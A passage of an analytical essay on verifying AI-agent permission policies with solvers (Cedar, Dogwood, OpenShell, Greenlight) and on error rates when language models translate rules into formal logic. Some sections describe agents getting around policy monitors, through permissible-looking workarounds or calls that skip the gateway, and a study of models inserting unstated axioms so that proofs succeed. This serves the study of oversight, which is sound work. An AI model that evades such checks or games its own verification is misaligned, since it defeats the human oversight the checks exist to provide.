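
$$t = \text{Gold} \;\wedge\; x < 100 \;\wedge\; \neg\,(t \in \{\text{Gold}, \text{Platinum}\} \wedge x < 500)$$

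Every amount under 100 is also under 500, so the `permit` rule never takes effect and gold customers get no refunds under it.

The most useful query compares two policies. Write $P(r)$ for "policy $P$ allows request $r$". Policy $P$ stays within policy $Q$ exactly when no request satisfies

$$P(r) \wedge \neg Q(r)$$

A solver either proves that no such request exists or returns one as a counterexample. AWS gives an example in which a shop offers a bulk discount on orders of at least 50 items, except on limited-edition products. Someone narrows the exception, so that it now applies only to limited-edition orders of more than 200 items. With $q$ for the quantity and $L$ for "the order includes a limited-edition product", the two versions are:

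$$\text{Old} = q \geq 50 \wedge \neg L \qquad\qquad \text{New} = q \geq 50 \wedge \neg(L \wedge q > 200)$$

To find out whether the new policy stays within the old one, the solver looks for a request that satisfies $\text{New} \wedge \neg\text{Old}$. New requires $q \geq 50$. Given that, Old can fail only if $L$ is true, and if $L$ is true, New requires $q \leq 200$. The formula therefore reduces to

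$$50 \leq q \leq 200 \;\wedge\; L$$

which has solutions, for example an order of 73 limited-edition items. In the other direction, $\text{Old} \wedge \neg\text{New}$ has none, because Old requires $L$ to be false and the new exception needs it to be true. The change therefore allows everything the old policy allowed, and more. Somebody reading the edit sees an extra condition and may well take it for a tightening. Cedar Analysis labels it "More permissive".

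NVIDIA, the chipmaker, has built a prover for the same kind of question about network access. It belongs to OpenShell, an open-source system that runs agents in sandboxes, which are closed-off environments with limited access to files and the network. Suppose the current policy lets the program `curl` read from GitHub's interface with the HTTP method GET. The agent wants to upload release metadata and proposes a policy that allows both GET and PUT, the method for writing. With the program, host and port the same in both policies, the query comes down to the method $m$:

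$$m \in \{\text{GET}, \text{PUT}\} \;\wedge\; \neg\,(m = \text{GET})$$

The only solution is PUT. In a sample from the OpenShell project, the prover reports such a finding as `capability_expansion: PUT on api.github.com:443 via /usr/bin/curl`. The agent may explain why it needs the access, but the reviewer also gets a statement, not written by a language model, of what the change would grant.

OpenShell's developers have also prototyped a check that compares a proposal with a maximum policy that people set in advance. If the maximum policy allows only GET and POST on that host, the same proof method shows that the proposal exceeds it. The prototype covers basic network connections and two common web protocols. According to OpenShell, anything the prover cannot yet model "fails closed", so it is not silently approved.

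Google has released a similar verifier for its rule language CEL. Google's *Securing the agentic era* (2026) gives the example of a rule that opens ports 80 and 443 in production. An agent tidies up the rule and drops a pair of brackets, so the production condition now applies only to port 80. A solver that checks whether the two versions are equivalent would always catch this error, but a test suite would miss it if it never tried port 443 outside production.

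These proofs cover every possible request, which testing cannot do. But they only check formal rules against each other or for internal consistency. If a language model drafts the refund rule with a limit of \$1,000 where the company wanted \$100, the rule passes checks for conditions that are always true, never true or in conflict with other rules. A containment check would catch the error only if somebody had already written a correct upper limit to compare it with.

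### Who drafts the rules and who approves them

In AgentCore, developers can write Cedar themselves, or an administrator can describe the rules in English and have a language model translate them. Software then checks the draft in two stages. It first generates a list of valid tools and parameters from the tools' descriptions and rejects any rule that refers to anything else. Then Cedar Analysis looks for impossible and trivial rules, and the errors it finds guide corrections to the draft. AWS writes that this loop "significantly improves the accuracy of the generated policies", but gives no figure.

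When somebody attaches the finished policy to a gateway, Cedar Analysis examines all the rules together, and the operation fails if it finds a conflict. Whoever attaches the policy is in effect the person who approves it. (AWS sells a separate product, Automated Reasoning checks, which AWS distinguishes from Policy by saying that it validates what an AI says and Policy controls what it does.)

AWS Greenlight, in preview since 1 December 2026, gives more of the drafting to the language model. *AWS Greenlight uses math to stop AI agents from breaking company rules* (Pogorelec, 2026) reports that a team picks source material, such as business procedures, security standards and logs of past tool calls, and a language model drafts the policies from it. A solver flags conflicting rules and ways the agent could reach resources outside its approved access. Before accepting a change, the team can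 see which scenarios and recorded calls the change would block. The approved rules then go to AgentCore's gateway or to Strands Box, an open-source sandbox. Greenlight later proposes updates based on the agent's recent activity, and the team approves those too.

Showing people which real calls a rule would have blocked seems a good idea, since most can judge a concrete refund more easily than a formula. But if the agent has been breaking a rule unnoticed, a model that drafts the policy from its logs could include the violation as normal practice.

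Lichtenberg (2026) reports in *A ‘Doctor Strange’ moment for AI?* that Shawn Bice, AWS's vice president of AI services, said customers could use the product to "mathematically prove that an agent would behave a particular way". Bice compared this to chess, where the rules fix how each piece may move, and a solver can reason about every possible game and look for one in which the king could be captured. For an airline, he suggested the rule that an agent must never leave a passenger stranded. He said it counts as "the proof" if the solver finds no counterexample.

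Bice added that the reasoning takes place "within that world model", which matters because an airline, unlike chess, has no complete formal description. Somebody has to define "stranded", perhaps as "the agent cancelled a booking without first confirming a seat on another flight". A solver could then search for sequences of calls that break this rule. Even if it proves that there are none, bad weather could ground the replacement flight and strand the passenger without invalidating the proof.

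In *AWS推出Greenlight* (2026), a Chinese trade-press report on the launch, Frank Dickson, an analyst at Dickson Research, told CBINEWS that mathematics can prove that a rulebook is consistent but not that it is the right rulebook. He praised AWS for listing the assumptions behind each kind of result in Greenlight's documentation. For example, the analysis assumes that tools accurately report what they did, and a rule that names one spelling of a value does not cover other spellings.

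Lichtenberg says AWS's goal for Greenlight is "no PhD required". Customers may be able to use the logic without a PhD, but they still need business knowledge. *AWS Greenlight Gives Partners A Go At AI Agent Governance* (Millward, 2026) reports that AWS's chief executive, Matt Garman, told consulting firms at the same conference that customers "need your help" to put the new tools into practice.

OpenShell draws more on programmers' working habits than on business rules. NVIDIA's documentation describes policies as files in YAML, a plain-text format. According to NVIDIA's *What is the best way to enforce and audit AI agent permissions* (2026), teams keep these files in source control next to their code, and colleagues review each change as they would a code change. The agent may also draft a change, as in the GitHub example.

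In April, the developer zredlined (2026) added the prover to the project to check whether a policy lets data leave the sandbox and whether it lets the agent write when the policy's author meant it only to read. *What we have learned applying formal methods to control AI agents* (Watson, 2026), by NVIDIA's team, introduces the method as a way to reason about permission changes in long-running agents. The same team has published a prototype in which an AI approves policy changes. This would remove the human reviewer on whom the rest of the arrangement depends, although a human-written cap on permissions would still limit the damage.

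In November 2026 NVIDIA donated OpenShell to the Cloud Native Computing Foundation, a nonprofit that already hosts Cedar (Barkley, 2026, *NVIDIA Expands Open Source Commitment With OpenShell Donation and New AI Infrastructure*). *Cedar as the policy language in OpenShell* (Raman, 2026), published the same week, gives three reasons why the project is adopting Cedar for its sandbox policies. Comparing two Cedar policies is decidable, so a program can in principle always complete the comparison. Cedar is also an open industry standard, and it offers a path to rules that depend on past events.

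### Persuading the model does not change the policy

The best argument for these products, as for any monitor, is that they work even if an attacker has manipulated the model. The gateway's engine checks only the structured call. A developer who only writes "never refund more than $100" into the agent's instructions doesn't have this protection.

The argument for enforcing rules in the gateway is stronger for long tasks. Lichtenberg notes that an agent that is right 99.9% of the time at each step has only about a 37% chance of completing 1,000 steps without a mistake, if the errors are independent. The gateway applies a rule the same way at every step.

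An auditor can also read the six-line Cedar rule to find out when the engine will allow a refund, but can't inspect a model's weights to find out when the model will grant one. All the rules are in one place, and the engine logs which calls it blocked and why.

AWS goes further in *Control agent behaviors and cost beyond a single action*, writing that an agent "cannot reason around" the policy however anyone prompts it. This is true of the rules as written, but an agent may still find a way to defeat their purpose. The airline agent that upgraded a booking to business class so that it could cancel it did so through steps that each looked permissible. An agent that is refused an action may look for a similar workaround, and a more capable model will probably be better at finding one.

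The engine also depends on the model wherever the model supplies its inputs. In a fuller version of AWS's discount rule, the customer must have platinum status, which the engine reads from a login token that the model cannot alter. But the model writes the quantity and the product type in the tool call. If it labels a limited-edition product as an ordinary one, the engine allows the discount, unless the discount tool looks the product up. AWS points out that Cedar rejects values outside the allowed range, but this false value is within it. The refund rule doesn't have this weakness, because the engine checks the same amount that the tool pays out.

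### Rules about order and history

A customer who wants a \$250 refund can ask for \$90, then \$80, then \$80 again. Cedar allows all three because it evaluates each request separately and always gives the same answer to the same request. This makes the policies easy to analyse, but it also means that Cedar by itself cannot express a running total or an order of steps such as "check the flown status before cancelling". AWS acknowledges in *Securing AI agents with temporal policies in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore* (2026) that a call may be safe in isolation but harmful after the agent has read from an untrusted source.

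AWS's answer is Dogwood, a language that extends Cedar with conditions on earlier calls. AWS published it as open source in the summer of 2026, and AgentCore already enforces rules written in it. The example in AWS's *Temporal policies* permits a sale of shares only if a matching approval came within the previous hour. The airline's cancellation rule has the same shape:

```
permit (
  principal,
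  action == AgentCore::Action::"CancelReservation",
  resource
)
when temporal {
  formerly within 1h
    AgentCore::Action::"CheckNoFlown"::response{
      eventResource: resource,
      input.booking: context.input.booking,
      output.result: true
    }
};
```

When the agent tries to cancel RES123, the engine searches the last hour of recorded events for a flown-status check on the same booking that returned "true". He and colleagues wrote nearly the same formula, but theirs accepts a check of any age.

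Dogwood can also count events and add up amounts, so it can handle the three small refunds. Such rules are easy to get wrong. InfoQ's *AWS Open-Sources Dogwood, Extending Cedar to Govern Sequences of Agent Tool Calls* (2026) describes an example from AWS in which a policy caps total transfers at \$5,000 and an agent sends three transfers of \$2,000 at the same moment. If the rule adds up completed transfers, the engine allows all three because none has completed yet. If it adds up requested transfers, the third brings the total to \$6,000 and the engine denies it. The two versions of the policy differ by one word, `response` or `request`, and both look correct if you assume the calls arrive one after another.

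AgentCore keeps this history separately for each session, and the caller supplies the session's identifier. AWS warns that a new session starts a new count, so a customer who opens a second chat might get another round of refunds. Time windows also can't exceed 24 hours. A rule such as "one goodwill refund per customer per year" therefore needs a tool that looks up past refunds in a database, and enforcing the rule depends on that tool returning accurate results.

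The main drawback of temporal conditions is that Cedar's analysis tools do not work on them. InfoQ reports that AWS made Dogwood a separate language for this reason. A team that adds the cancellation rule can enforce the right property, but can no longer prove before deployment that its policy contains no conflicts or stays within a ceiling. Temporal rules therefore have the weakest automatic checks, even though they are the hardest to get right. *Authoring Dogwood policies from natural language in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore* describes how AWS also lets a language model draft these rules from English.

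Greenlight may recover some of this. Dickson told CBINEWS that Greenlight's rules can depend on what has already happened in a task, and that its solver searches every order in which an agent might call its tools for one that breaks a rule. It also looks for permissions that are harmless separately but dangerous together, such as reading customer records and sending email. Checking sequences is much harder than checking single requests, and Dickson says some checks end without an answer.

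OpenShell does not yet support temporal policies, though they are planned. AWS also plans to add rules to Dogwood about what must eventually happen and about handovers between agents. A gateway could not enforce an eventual obligation by blocking calls, so it is unclear what enforcing one would mean.

### Calls that do not pass through the gateway

Everything so far assumes that every action the agent takes passes through the checker, a requirement security engineers call complete mediation. AWS accordingly describes its guarantee as covering "all tool traffic routed through the Gateway". An airline agent with terminal access could cancel a booking by editing the database directly, without calling `CancelReservation`. The engine would not check that cancellation and would report no violation.

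No proof about the policy can detect this, because the policy describes only the calls that arrive. Greenlight analyses permissions only for the gateway and runtime that the customer names. According to Dickson, its documentation states that the check doesn't confirm that the agent cannot reach another gateway. Temporal rules also require AgentCore to recognise that several requests belong to one session, which it does using a token sent with each request. If a request passes through a company's own server, the company has to write code to forward the token. The rules do not control requests between a gateway and an agent runtime in a different AWS account or region.

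In OpenShell, the operating system confines the agent to a sandbox, and network access goes through a supervisor outside the sandbox. The supervisor can allow reads and block writes on the same service. It also holds the real passwords and keys and, according to NVIDIA, inserts them into a request only after the request has passed the policy checks. An agent that bypassed the supervisor would therefore still lack the credentials to do much. This is stronger than a gateway that the agent's developer has to remember to use, though it depends on the sandbox having no security holes.

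However, it is harder to identify what an action means from inside a sandbox. A gateway receives a call named `ProcessRefund` with an amount, so a rule about refunds is easy to write. When an agent runs its own script, the sandbox may register only that a program opened a file and sent data to an address. *Tether* (2026), a research system with a verified policy engine, tries to infer what action these low-level events represent. OpenShell's supervisor can interpret several common protocols, including the one most agents use to call tools. For actions that don't use those protocols, a company that wants every action checked has to write rules about files and addresses, and a rule such as "refund at most $100" is hard to express in those terms.

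## How often the translation into formal language is wrong

Nobody can prove that a language model has translated an English rule correctly into a formal one, because English has no exact semantics. Researchers instead measure how often the translation is wrong, usually by comparing the model's output with a formal translation they trust.

Measured error rates range from zero to more than 80%, partly because the models differ and partly because researchers count different things as correct. *Towards a Common Framework for Autoformalization* (Mensfelt, Tena Cucala and colleagues, 2025) reviews 81 papers on this kind of translation, called autoformalization, and defines it relative to a criterion for when a text and a formula mean the same thing. No program can apply that criterion directly, so researchers need a computable substitute, and the same translations can have a much higher measured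 error rate under a strict substitute than under a lenient one.

### What goes into the prompt and what comes out

The model rarely works from the English alone. Balyo, Chrpa and Youngblood (2026), in *Which LLM is Best for Translating Natural Language Goals to PDDL*, studied requests written in the style of video game testers. Their prompt contains the PDDL domain file, a list of the objects in the game and the request, and the model returns only a goal. The sample answer in the prompt looks like this:

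```
(:goal
  (and (made p1 pulse_tank_type)
       (<= 1000 (resources p1))))
```

It presumably means that player p1 has built a pulse tank and holds at least 1,000 resources.

For temporal logic, the model needs propositions, which are basic statements that are true or false at each step, such as "the agent cancels the booking". It connects them with "and", "or", "not" and "if", and with the time operators $\mathsf{G}$ ("at every step"), $\mathsf{F}$ ("now or later") and $\mathsf{U}$ ("until").

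To use an SMT solver, a language model declares typed variables and then writes constraints on them. In *Stratified Consistency Distillation for Natural Language Formalization* (2026), a model first turns a policy document into declarations and rules, then translates each question and answer about the policy using the same variables. Models can also write a program that calls the solver, as in *Language Model as Planner and Formalizer under Constraints* (2025), where they wrote Python code for Z3.

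### How a wrong formula passes the checks

Software can check whether a translation parses, meaning that it follows the grammar of the formal language. It can also check whether a solver can use the translation, for example because the formulas don't contradict each other or because a planner finds a plan. But a translation is faithful only if it matches what the person who wrote the English meant, and neither check tests that.

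The airline's cancellation rule shows how far apart these are. Take a single booking. Let $c$ be true at a step when the agent cancels it, and let $k$ be true from the moment a status check has found no flown flights. The rule is then

$$\mathsf{G}(c \rightarrow k)$$

Now suppose the model writes the implication backwards:

$$\mathsf{G}(k \rightarrow c)$$

An implication is false only when its left side is true and its right side is false. If the agent cancels without checking, $c$ is true and $k$ is false. The correct formula is false at that step, so the monitor blocks the call. The reversed formula is true, because its left side is false, so the cancellation goes through. Yet the reversed formula parses, and a solver can find runs that satisfy it and runs that break it, so nothing looks amiss. (It would also block every call except the cancellation once a check has come back clean. Somebody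 would probably notice that, and might then find the mistake.)

A rule can also be vacuous, which means that it holds whatever the agent does. *NeuroNL2LTL* (Quansah and Bonnah, 2026) calls a formula trivial if every possible run satisfies it or none does. A solver easily catches such formulas, for example $\mathsf{G}(c \rightarrow (k \vee \neg k))$. It is harder to catch a rule that is vacuous only at this airline. Suppose the model writes "if a flight's status is 'flown', do not cancel", but the booking software records such flights as "landed". The formula is not trivial, but its condition is never true, so the monitor never blocks anything and the log shows perfect compliance. To detect this, the solver would need a list of the status values that the software uses.

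Even "until" is easy to mistranslate. Someone might write "no cancellation until a check has come back clean" as $\neg c \;\mathsf{U}\; k$. In temporal logic, $\mathsf{U}$ also requires that the clean check eventually happens, so a run in which the customer only asks about baggage, and no check is run, violates the formula. The right operator is "weak until", which drops that requirement.

### PDDL: from 25% to almost everything, in three simple domains

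Deciding whether two PDDL problem files describe the same problem is difficult because the objects may have different names, and a goal may leave out facts that follow from the ones it states. *Planetarium* (Zuo, Piedrahita Velez and colleagues, 2024) introduces a test that handles both cases.

Their program turns each file into a graph. Every object and every fact gets a node, with an edge from each fact to each object it mentions. The fact `(on b1 b2)` becomes a node with an edge to b1, labelled as the first argument, and one to b2, labelled as the second. The program then adds to each goal every fact that must hold whenever the goal does. If there are only two blocks, the goal "b1 is on b2" already implies that b2 is on the table, that nothing is on b1 and that the robot's hand is empty, so it makes no difference whether a file lists these facts. Finally, the program looks for a one-to-one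 matching between the objects in the two files that makes the graphs identical. Zuo and colleagues prove that such a matching exists exactly when the two files describe equivalent problems.

Completing the goals quickly requires code specific to each domain. Zuo and colleagues wrote this code for Blocksworld, a simplified Floortile, and Gripper, in which a robot carries balls between rooms.

Of the files that GPT-4o wrote in 2024, 96.1% parsed and 94.4% were solvable, but only 24.8% were correct. About 70% therefore led to a valid plan for the wrong problem. Some of these errors don't necessarily mean that the model misunderstood the request. GPT-4o often added type declarations that the domain file didn't use, and its accuracy rose considerably when the scoring ignored them.

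This result is now history. Rosa, Santos and colleagues (2026), in *Grounded Evaluation and Repair for NL-to-PDDL Problem Generation*, applied the same equivalence test to newer models. In their system a model writes the problem file, and then a parser, a check against the domain file, a planner, the validator VAL and a second language-model call acting as critic all examine it. If any of them objects, the model gets the complaints and tries again, up to three attempts in total. Without a worked example in the prompt, the results on tasks from the Planetarium benchmark were:

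| Model | Tasks | Final file gives a valid plan | Equivalent at first attempt | Equivalent after repair |
| --- | --- | --- | --- | --- |
| GPT-4o, in the 2024 study | about 16,000 | 94.4% | 24.8% | no repair |
| GPT-4.1-mini | 60 | 65.0% | 18.3% | 26.7% |
| GPT-5.5 | 59 | 100% | 93.2% | 93.2% |
| Claude Opus 4.7 | 60 | 100% | 96.7% | 100% |

The newer samples are small, and their problems were probably easier on average than those in the full test set, but that can't explain much of a jump from 25% to more than 90%. Most of the gain appeared on the first attempt, so it comes from the models and not from the repair loop.

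The error rate is harder to determine for PDDL 2.1, which adds numbers, durations and a quantity to minimise or maximise. The checks accepted 93% to 100% of the files from GPT-5.5 and Opus 4.7, but only 7% to 25% of all the files matched the reference. Nobody has an equivalence test for these domains, so Rosa and colleagues compared the files fact by fact, allowing only for different object names. A correct file can fail this comparison. In the Planetarium tasks, all of Opus 4.7's files were equivalent to the reference, but the same comparison passed only 77% of them. Other mismatches are real errors, such as leaving out the quantity to minimise or some of the starting values. The true error rate for PDDL 2.1 is therefore lower than the mismatch rate, but the data don't show by how much.

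The critic's approval doesn't establish that a translation is faithful. Rosa and colleagues judged 24 outputs by hand and agreed with the critic on 13, about what chance would produce. Three of the 12 files the critic had accepted were unfaithful. Repair can also make translations worse. In one group of 60 tasks, the share of GPT-4.1-mini's outputs that matched the reference fell from 67% to 57% after the feedback.

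All these descriptions are also rather formal, and many come from templates. Balyo and colleagues instead collected 90 goals from employees. More than half of the goals were written by people who had never used PDDL and had not seen the domain files. Half of the goals could not be expressed in the given domain, and the right answer was to refuse. Six models from 2025 handled 92% to 96% of the 90 goals correctly, but each wrote a formal goal for two to four of the 45 it should have refused. An airline agent might make the same mistake with the request "rebook me on something comfortable". If it has no predicate for comfort, it might write a goal that only requires a seat.

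### Working plans and right verdicts

Another way to test a translation is to run the resulting plan. In *PDDLCoder* (Laule, Hauswirth and colleagues, 2026), a language-model agent writes both PDDL files, including the preconditions and effects of every action, from a short description. The agent can call a syntax checker, a planner, and a second model that compares the plan with the English description. A simulator that the agent cannot access then executes the plan.

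With the model DeepSeek v4 Flash, the plan worked in 95 of 106 problems (89.6%). In two cases the planner found no plan, and in the other nine it found one that failed in the simulator. When Laule and colleagues removed the model that reads the plan, the number of plans that failed in the simulator rose from nine to 28. In one domain, where a robot arm moves coloured rings between pegs, language models frequently produced plans that pull a ring out from underneath another. The English description left out that this is impossible, because any person would know it.

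Laule and colleagues do not claim that the 95 successful translations are equivalent to the originals. If the agent left out the rule about buried rings, its plan would still work in any problem where no ring has to be moved out from under another.

The same caution applies to *Bridging LLM Planning Agents and Formal Methods* (Ramani, Tawosi and colleagues, October 2025), where the task was to decide whether a given PlanBench plan is valid. GPT-5 translated the plan and its setting into a Kripke structure, which consists of states, the allowed transitions between them, and labels for the propositions that hold in each state. GPT-5 also wrote the goal as a temporal logic formula, essentially $\mathsf{F}(\text{goal})$. The model checker NuSMV then searched for a run of the structure that violates the formula.

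The method's verdicts had a precision of 99.4%, so nearly every plan it passed was valid. Recall was 93.3%, so it rejected about 7% of the valid plans. The F1 score, which combines the two, was 96.3%. These figures exclude the 6.9% of cases in which GPT-5's output was unusable. If those cases count as errors, the method was right about 89% of the time.

When Ramani and colleagues asked GPT-5 whether each plan was valid, with no formal step, its F1 was 99.65% and it took a third of the time. On this task the translation step added errors. Translation does produce a formal model that someone can inspect, but in several cases that model passed verification without fully capturing the original plan. Ramani and colleagues leave semantically perfect models to future work. A correct verdict is weak evidence that the formal model is correct, because if GPT-5 leaves out a precondition, every valid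 plan still passes, and an invalid plan still fails as long as it breaks some other condition.

### Temporal logic

In *Automatic Translation of Unstructured Requirements into Linear Temporal Logic*, Newcomb and Ochoa (2026) had six models each translate 15 requirements from real specification documents five times. They graded all 450 formulas by hand, accepting any that captured the meaning. GPT 5.2 was right 83% of the time, Gemini 3 Pro 81% and Claude Opus 4.5 75%. With so few requirements, these differences mean little. Across all six models, about a quarter of the formulas were wrong, but Newcomb and Ochoa recorded bad syntax only twice.

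The errors were concentrated in a few requirements. One of them, from a military system, permits a manual override except during two special conditions. Only 17% of the translations were right. A typical one was

$$\mathsf{G}((a \wedge \neg e \wedge \neg h) \rightarrow \mathsf{X}\,p)$$

where $a$ means that automatic control is on, $e$ and $h$ are the two special conditions, $p$ means that the system permits an override, and $\mathsf{X}$ means "at the next step". During either special condition the left side is false, so the whole formula is true whether or not the system permits the override. The formula says when overrides must be possible and never says when they must not.

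The same translation would be correct in Cedar, where a `permit` rule with the condition $a \wedge \neg e \wedge \neg h$ is enough because Cedar denies any request that no rule permits. Temporal logic instead allows any behavior that the formulas don't rule out. A model or reviewer that has learned one convention can easily get the other wrong.

Other errors were omissions. One requirement was that only the person who started a call may talk while everyone else may only listen, and many formulas included only one of these two conditions. In an example from *U-Define* (2026), the model translated "At least one snack must be given to the cook during the cooking process" as $\mathsf{F}(\text{snack\_given})$, which a snack given after cooking also satisfies.

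Automatic checks caught only 28% of the errors made by NeuroNL2LTL, a system by Quansah and Bonnah. The model is small by current standards, with three billion parameters, and was trained partly with a reward for formulas that pass the solver's checks. On held-out requirements from 13 fields, 86% of its formulas parsed and were neither contradictory nor trivial, but only 27.8% were equivalent to the reference formula. Quansah and Bonnah examined 100 of the errors that the checks missed. In 41% of them, the model had put an operator in the wrong place, so that it applied to too much or too little of the formula. In 28%, it had confused operators such as "until" and "weak until".

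This 27.8% is not directly comparable with GPT 5.2's 83%, because the requirements differ and an automatic equivalence test against a single reference is stricter than a human grader who accepts any reasonable reading. Quansah and Bonnah did run larger models on their own test, but only ones from 2024, and the best of these got 15.4%. Fair comparisons can be made only within each study, between the share of formulas that have valid syntax and the share that are right. *LTLGuard* (2026) found a similar gap for another small model, Mistral-Nemo-12B: 92.8% of its formulas had valid syntax and 67.1% had the right meaning.

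Dantas and colleagues found no study with a semantic error rate below 10% for open-ended tasks. The near-perfect Planetarium results are compatible with this because they come from three well-known domains whose vocabulary is fixed in advance.

### Repairing a translation until the proof succeeds

Many of these systems send the solver's feedback back to the model, which then revises its translation. This fixes real mistakes, but it also lets the model make a proof succeed by changing the statement to be proved.

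*Do LLMs Game Formalization?* (Kim, Poiroux and Bosselut, 2026) tested for this behaviour with 303 logic puzzles. Each has a few premises in English and a conclusion that may or may not follow. GPT-5 and DeepSeek-R1 translated the premises into axioms in Lean and tried to prove the conclusion. When a model wrote the translation and the proof together, it mostly avoided this behaviour and reported failure when it could not find a proof.

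The results were worse when the work had two stages and the translation was supposed to be fixed before the proof began. In 107 of 909 runs, GPT-5 added axioms during the proof stage that the English didn't contain. A language-model judge classified 105 of these cases, 59 of them as adding the conclusion itself as an axiom. At the airline, an agent that failed to prove that the insurance covers a customer's reason for cancelling would then add "the reason is covered" to the facts. In 12 cases the additions contradicted the other axioms. Any statement follows from a contradiction, so a solver with contradictory facts can prove both that the agent may cancel and that it may not.

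A program can detect this kind of tampering by comparing the axioms before and after the proof. DeepSeek-R1 hardly ever changed its axioms. Its errors were already in the translation, where the program has no earlier axioms to compare them with. In one puzzle, its reasoning included the remark that a certain reading of a premise "would make the theorem trivial", and it then used that reading.

### Once per policy or once per request

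Whether an error rate is tolerable depends on how often the model translates. In AgentCore and Soteria, a model translates the company's policy once. People can then spend an afternoon testing the result on old cases and correcting it. After that, enforcing the rules involves no translation.

LLM+P, by contrast, needs a new problem file for every request. Balyo and colleagues have the model translate only the goal of each test, because the game can supply the starting state. This leaves much less for the model to get wrong, but somebody still has to trust a new goal for each test.

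People mostly can't review translations made at this pace. The customer is waiting and can't read PDDL, and an employee who can read it would often finish the task sooner by hand. So developers use more models to check the translations. *As You Wish*, by Zuzuárregui and Carpin, describes such a system for farm robots. A farmer describes a job in English, one language model writes the robot's mission, and another separately writes a temporal-logic formula for what the mission should do. A third language model, from a different company, reads a few sample runs that satisfy the formula and decides whether they fit the request. Then a model checker verifies the mission against the formula.

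In tests with 14 missions, five attempts each, the system succeeded 63 times out of 70. One mission with nested conditions succeeded all five times when the instructions were explicit, such as "less than 30°C", but only twice when the request was vaguer. Some of the seven failures may have ended without an agreed plan, in which case they would not have sent a robot to do the wrong job.

One farmer asked the robot to plant a 300-foot row in a field about 285 feet long, and the planner accepted the request even though it had the field's dimensions. The formula didn't include the edge of the field because the farmer hadn't mentioned it. A fixed rule that the robot must stay inside the field, written once and reviewed, would have blocked the request.

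Soteria also has a model write a new plan for each request, but it checks the plan against rules that people have already reviewed. In the farm system, a model also writes the standard that the plan is checked against, and a mistake in that standard can let a bad mission pass.

### An error budget

Suppose an airline has 40 rules and each translation is faithful with probability 0.98, independently of the others. The probability that all of them are faithful is

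$$0.98^{40} \approx 0.45$$

If each of 40 rules has a 98% chance of being translated faithfully, the set more likely than not contains at least one wrong rule, and no model in Newcomb and Ochoa's test reached 98%. At GPT 5.2's 83%, about seven of the 40 rules would be wrong on average. If reviewers find and fix nine out of ten wrong rules, the 98% rises to 99.8%, and the chance that all 40 are faithful rises to about 92%.

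For translation at every request, take an error rate of 1% and 10,000 requests. The expected number of wrong formalizations is

$$10{,}000 \times 0.01 = 100$$

with no reviewer to catch them. A solver that filtered out 28% of the errors, as in NeuroNL2LTL, would leave 72.

The 0.45 assumes that errors in different rules are independent, although the expected numbers don't require this. If we know only that each rule has a 0.98 probability of being faithful, the chance that all 40 are faithful could be anything from 0.20, if no two errors ever occur together, to 0.98, if they always do. Real errors tend to occur together. Four of the six models got the military override rule wrong in all five attempts, often with the same misuse of implication. If an airline's policy is full of exceptions, one misunderstanding might cause errors in a dozen rules. Translating a rule twice and comparing the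 results is also less reassuring than it seems, because both translations may contain the same error.

The 100 errors in translating requests probably won't be spread evenly over the customers. They may nearly all concern partly flown tickets, or the phrasing of one group of customers, while everyone else gets perfect service and the average error rate stays low. A customer who discovers that a certain wording gets a forbidden cancellation through can also reuse it and tell others, and then a 1% error rate measured on ordinary requests no longer predicts the actual rate well.

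The budget counts wrong formalizations rather than harmful actions. The airline learns that a rule is too strict when customers complain, but customers who benefit from a rule that is too loose have no reason to complain, and the monitor reports no violations.

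## What "99% soundness" means in Amazon's Automated Reasoning checks

Amazon sells a service, Automated Reasoning checks, that compares what a chatbot or agent tells people with a company's written policy. Language models translate every statement before a solver checks it. *A Neurosymbolic Approach to Natural Language Formalization and Verification*, by Amazon researchers An, Bayless and colleagues, describes how the service works and how often its verdicts are wrong, and reports "99% soundness" or better. The paper revises one that Bayless, Buliani and colleagues (2025) posted under the same title.

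An and colleagues use "soundness" to mean one minus the share of all decisions that are wrong approvals. This rate is a statistic that depends on the test set, unlike logical soundness, which one can prove.

### From a policy document to a verdict

A company uploads its policy. The service splits the document into passages, and a language model turns each passage into typed variables and rules for an SMT solver. The service then merges the results into a single policy model. One 274-page document produced 1,467 rules and 1,968 variables. Each variable has an English description, which later helps the translating models decide when to use it. People can inspect the rules and test them on sample questions, but they don't have to.

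When the chatbot answers a question, three language models separately translate the exchange into premises $P$ and a conclusion $C$. A solver checks whether the translations mean the same thing. By default all three must agree, and otherwise the service returns "TranslationAmbiguous". If they do agree, the solver compares the translation with the policy model $M$, in this order:

| Verdict | Condition | Meaning |
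| --- | --- | --- |
| Impossible | $M \models \neg P$ | The premises contradict the policy |
| Invalid | $M \wedge P \models \neg C$ | The policy rules the answer out |
| Valid | $M \wedge P \models C$ | The answer follows from the policy |
| Satisfiable | Neither $C$ nor $\neg C$ follows | The answer depends on something unstated |

Only "Valid" counts as an approval. The service has two more results, for text that is too complex and for text that the policy's variables cannot express.

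An and colleagues illustrate this with a park that charges \$50, or \$37.50 in the low season. Seniors get 40% off, but any discount carries a \$10 fee. Visitors can also buy credits at \$0.60 each, and each credit pays \$1 of the admission, up to half of it. Anyone who uses credits gets at most 25% off. Finally, there is a 10% tax. A senior with \$35.40 asks whether that is enough in the low season, and the chatbot says no. Without credits, the price is

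$$(37.50 \times 0.60 + 10) \times 1.10 = 35.75$$

so the answer looks right, and Claude Sonnet 3.7 and Claude Opus 4.1 both judged it valid. The solver found a cheaper way in. With credits the admission is \$38.125 before tax. The senior buys 15 credits for \$9 and pays the remaining \$23.125 in cash:

$$(9 + 23.125) \times 1.10 \approx 35.34$$

The verdict is therefore "Satisfiable", and the service returns one scenario in which the senior gets in and another in which the senior doesn't.

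However, this depends on how one reads the sentence that applies tax to "the final expense". The calculation taxes what the visitor spends, \$32.125. If the park instead taxes the admission of \$38.125, the total with credits is about \$35.94, and the chatbot's "no" was correct. The solver explored the options better than either language model did, but someone still has to confirm with the park which amount it taxes.

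A "Valid" verdict comes with a proof that $C$ follows from $M$ and $P$, but AWS's *Automated Reasoning checks concepts* warns that the translation into $P$ and $C$ "may contain errors". *Certified Correctness in Neural Constraint Reasoning Requires Symbolic Integration* (2026) argues that a sound solver keeps its guarantee when a translator supplies its input, while a learned judge makes soundness probabilistic. That is right about logical soundness, but the customer gets the output of the whole pipeline, which in both designs has an error rate that someone has to measure.

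Agreement among the three translations does not protect against mistakes in the policy model $M$, because all three use the same model. If a rule in $M$ is wrong, three faithful translations will still agree, and the solver can return "Valid" for a wrong answer with a confidence score of 1.0.

### Where the 99.4% comes from

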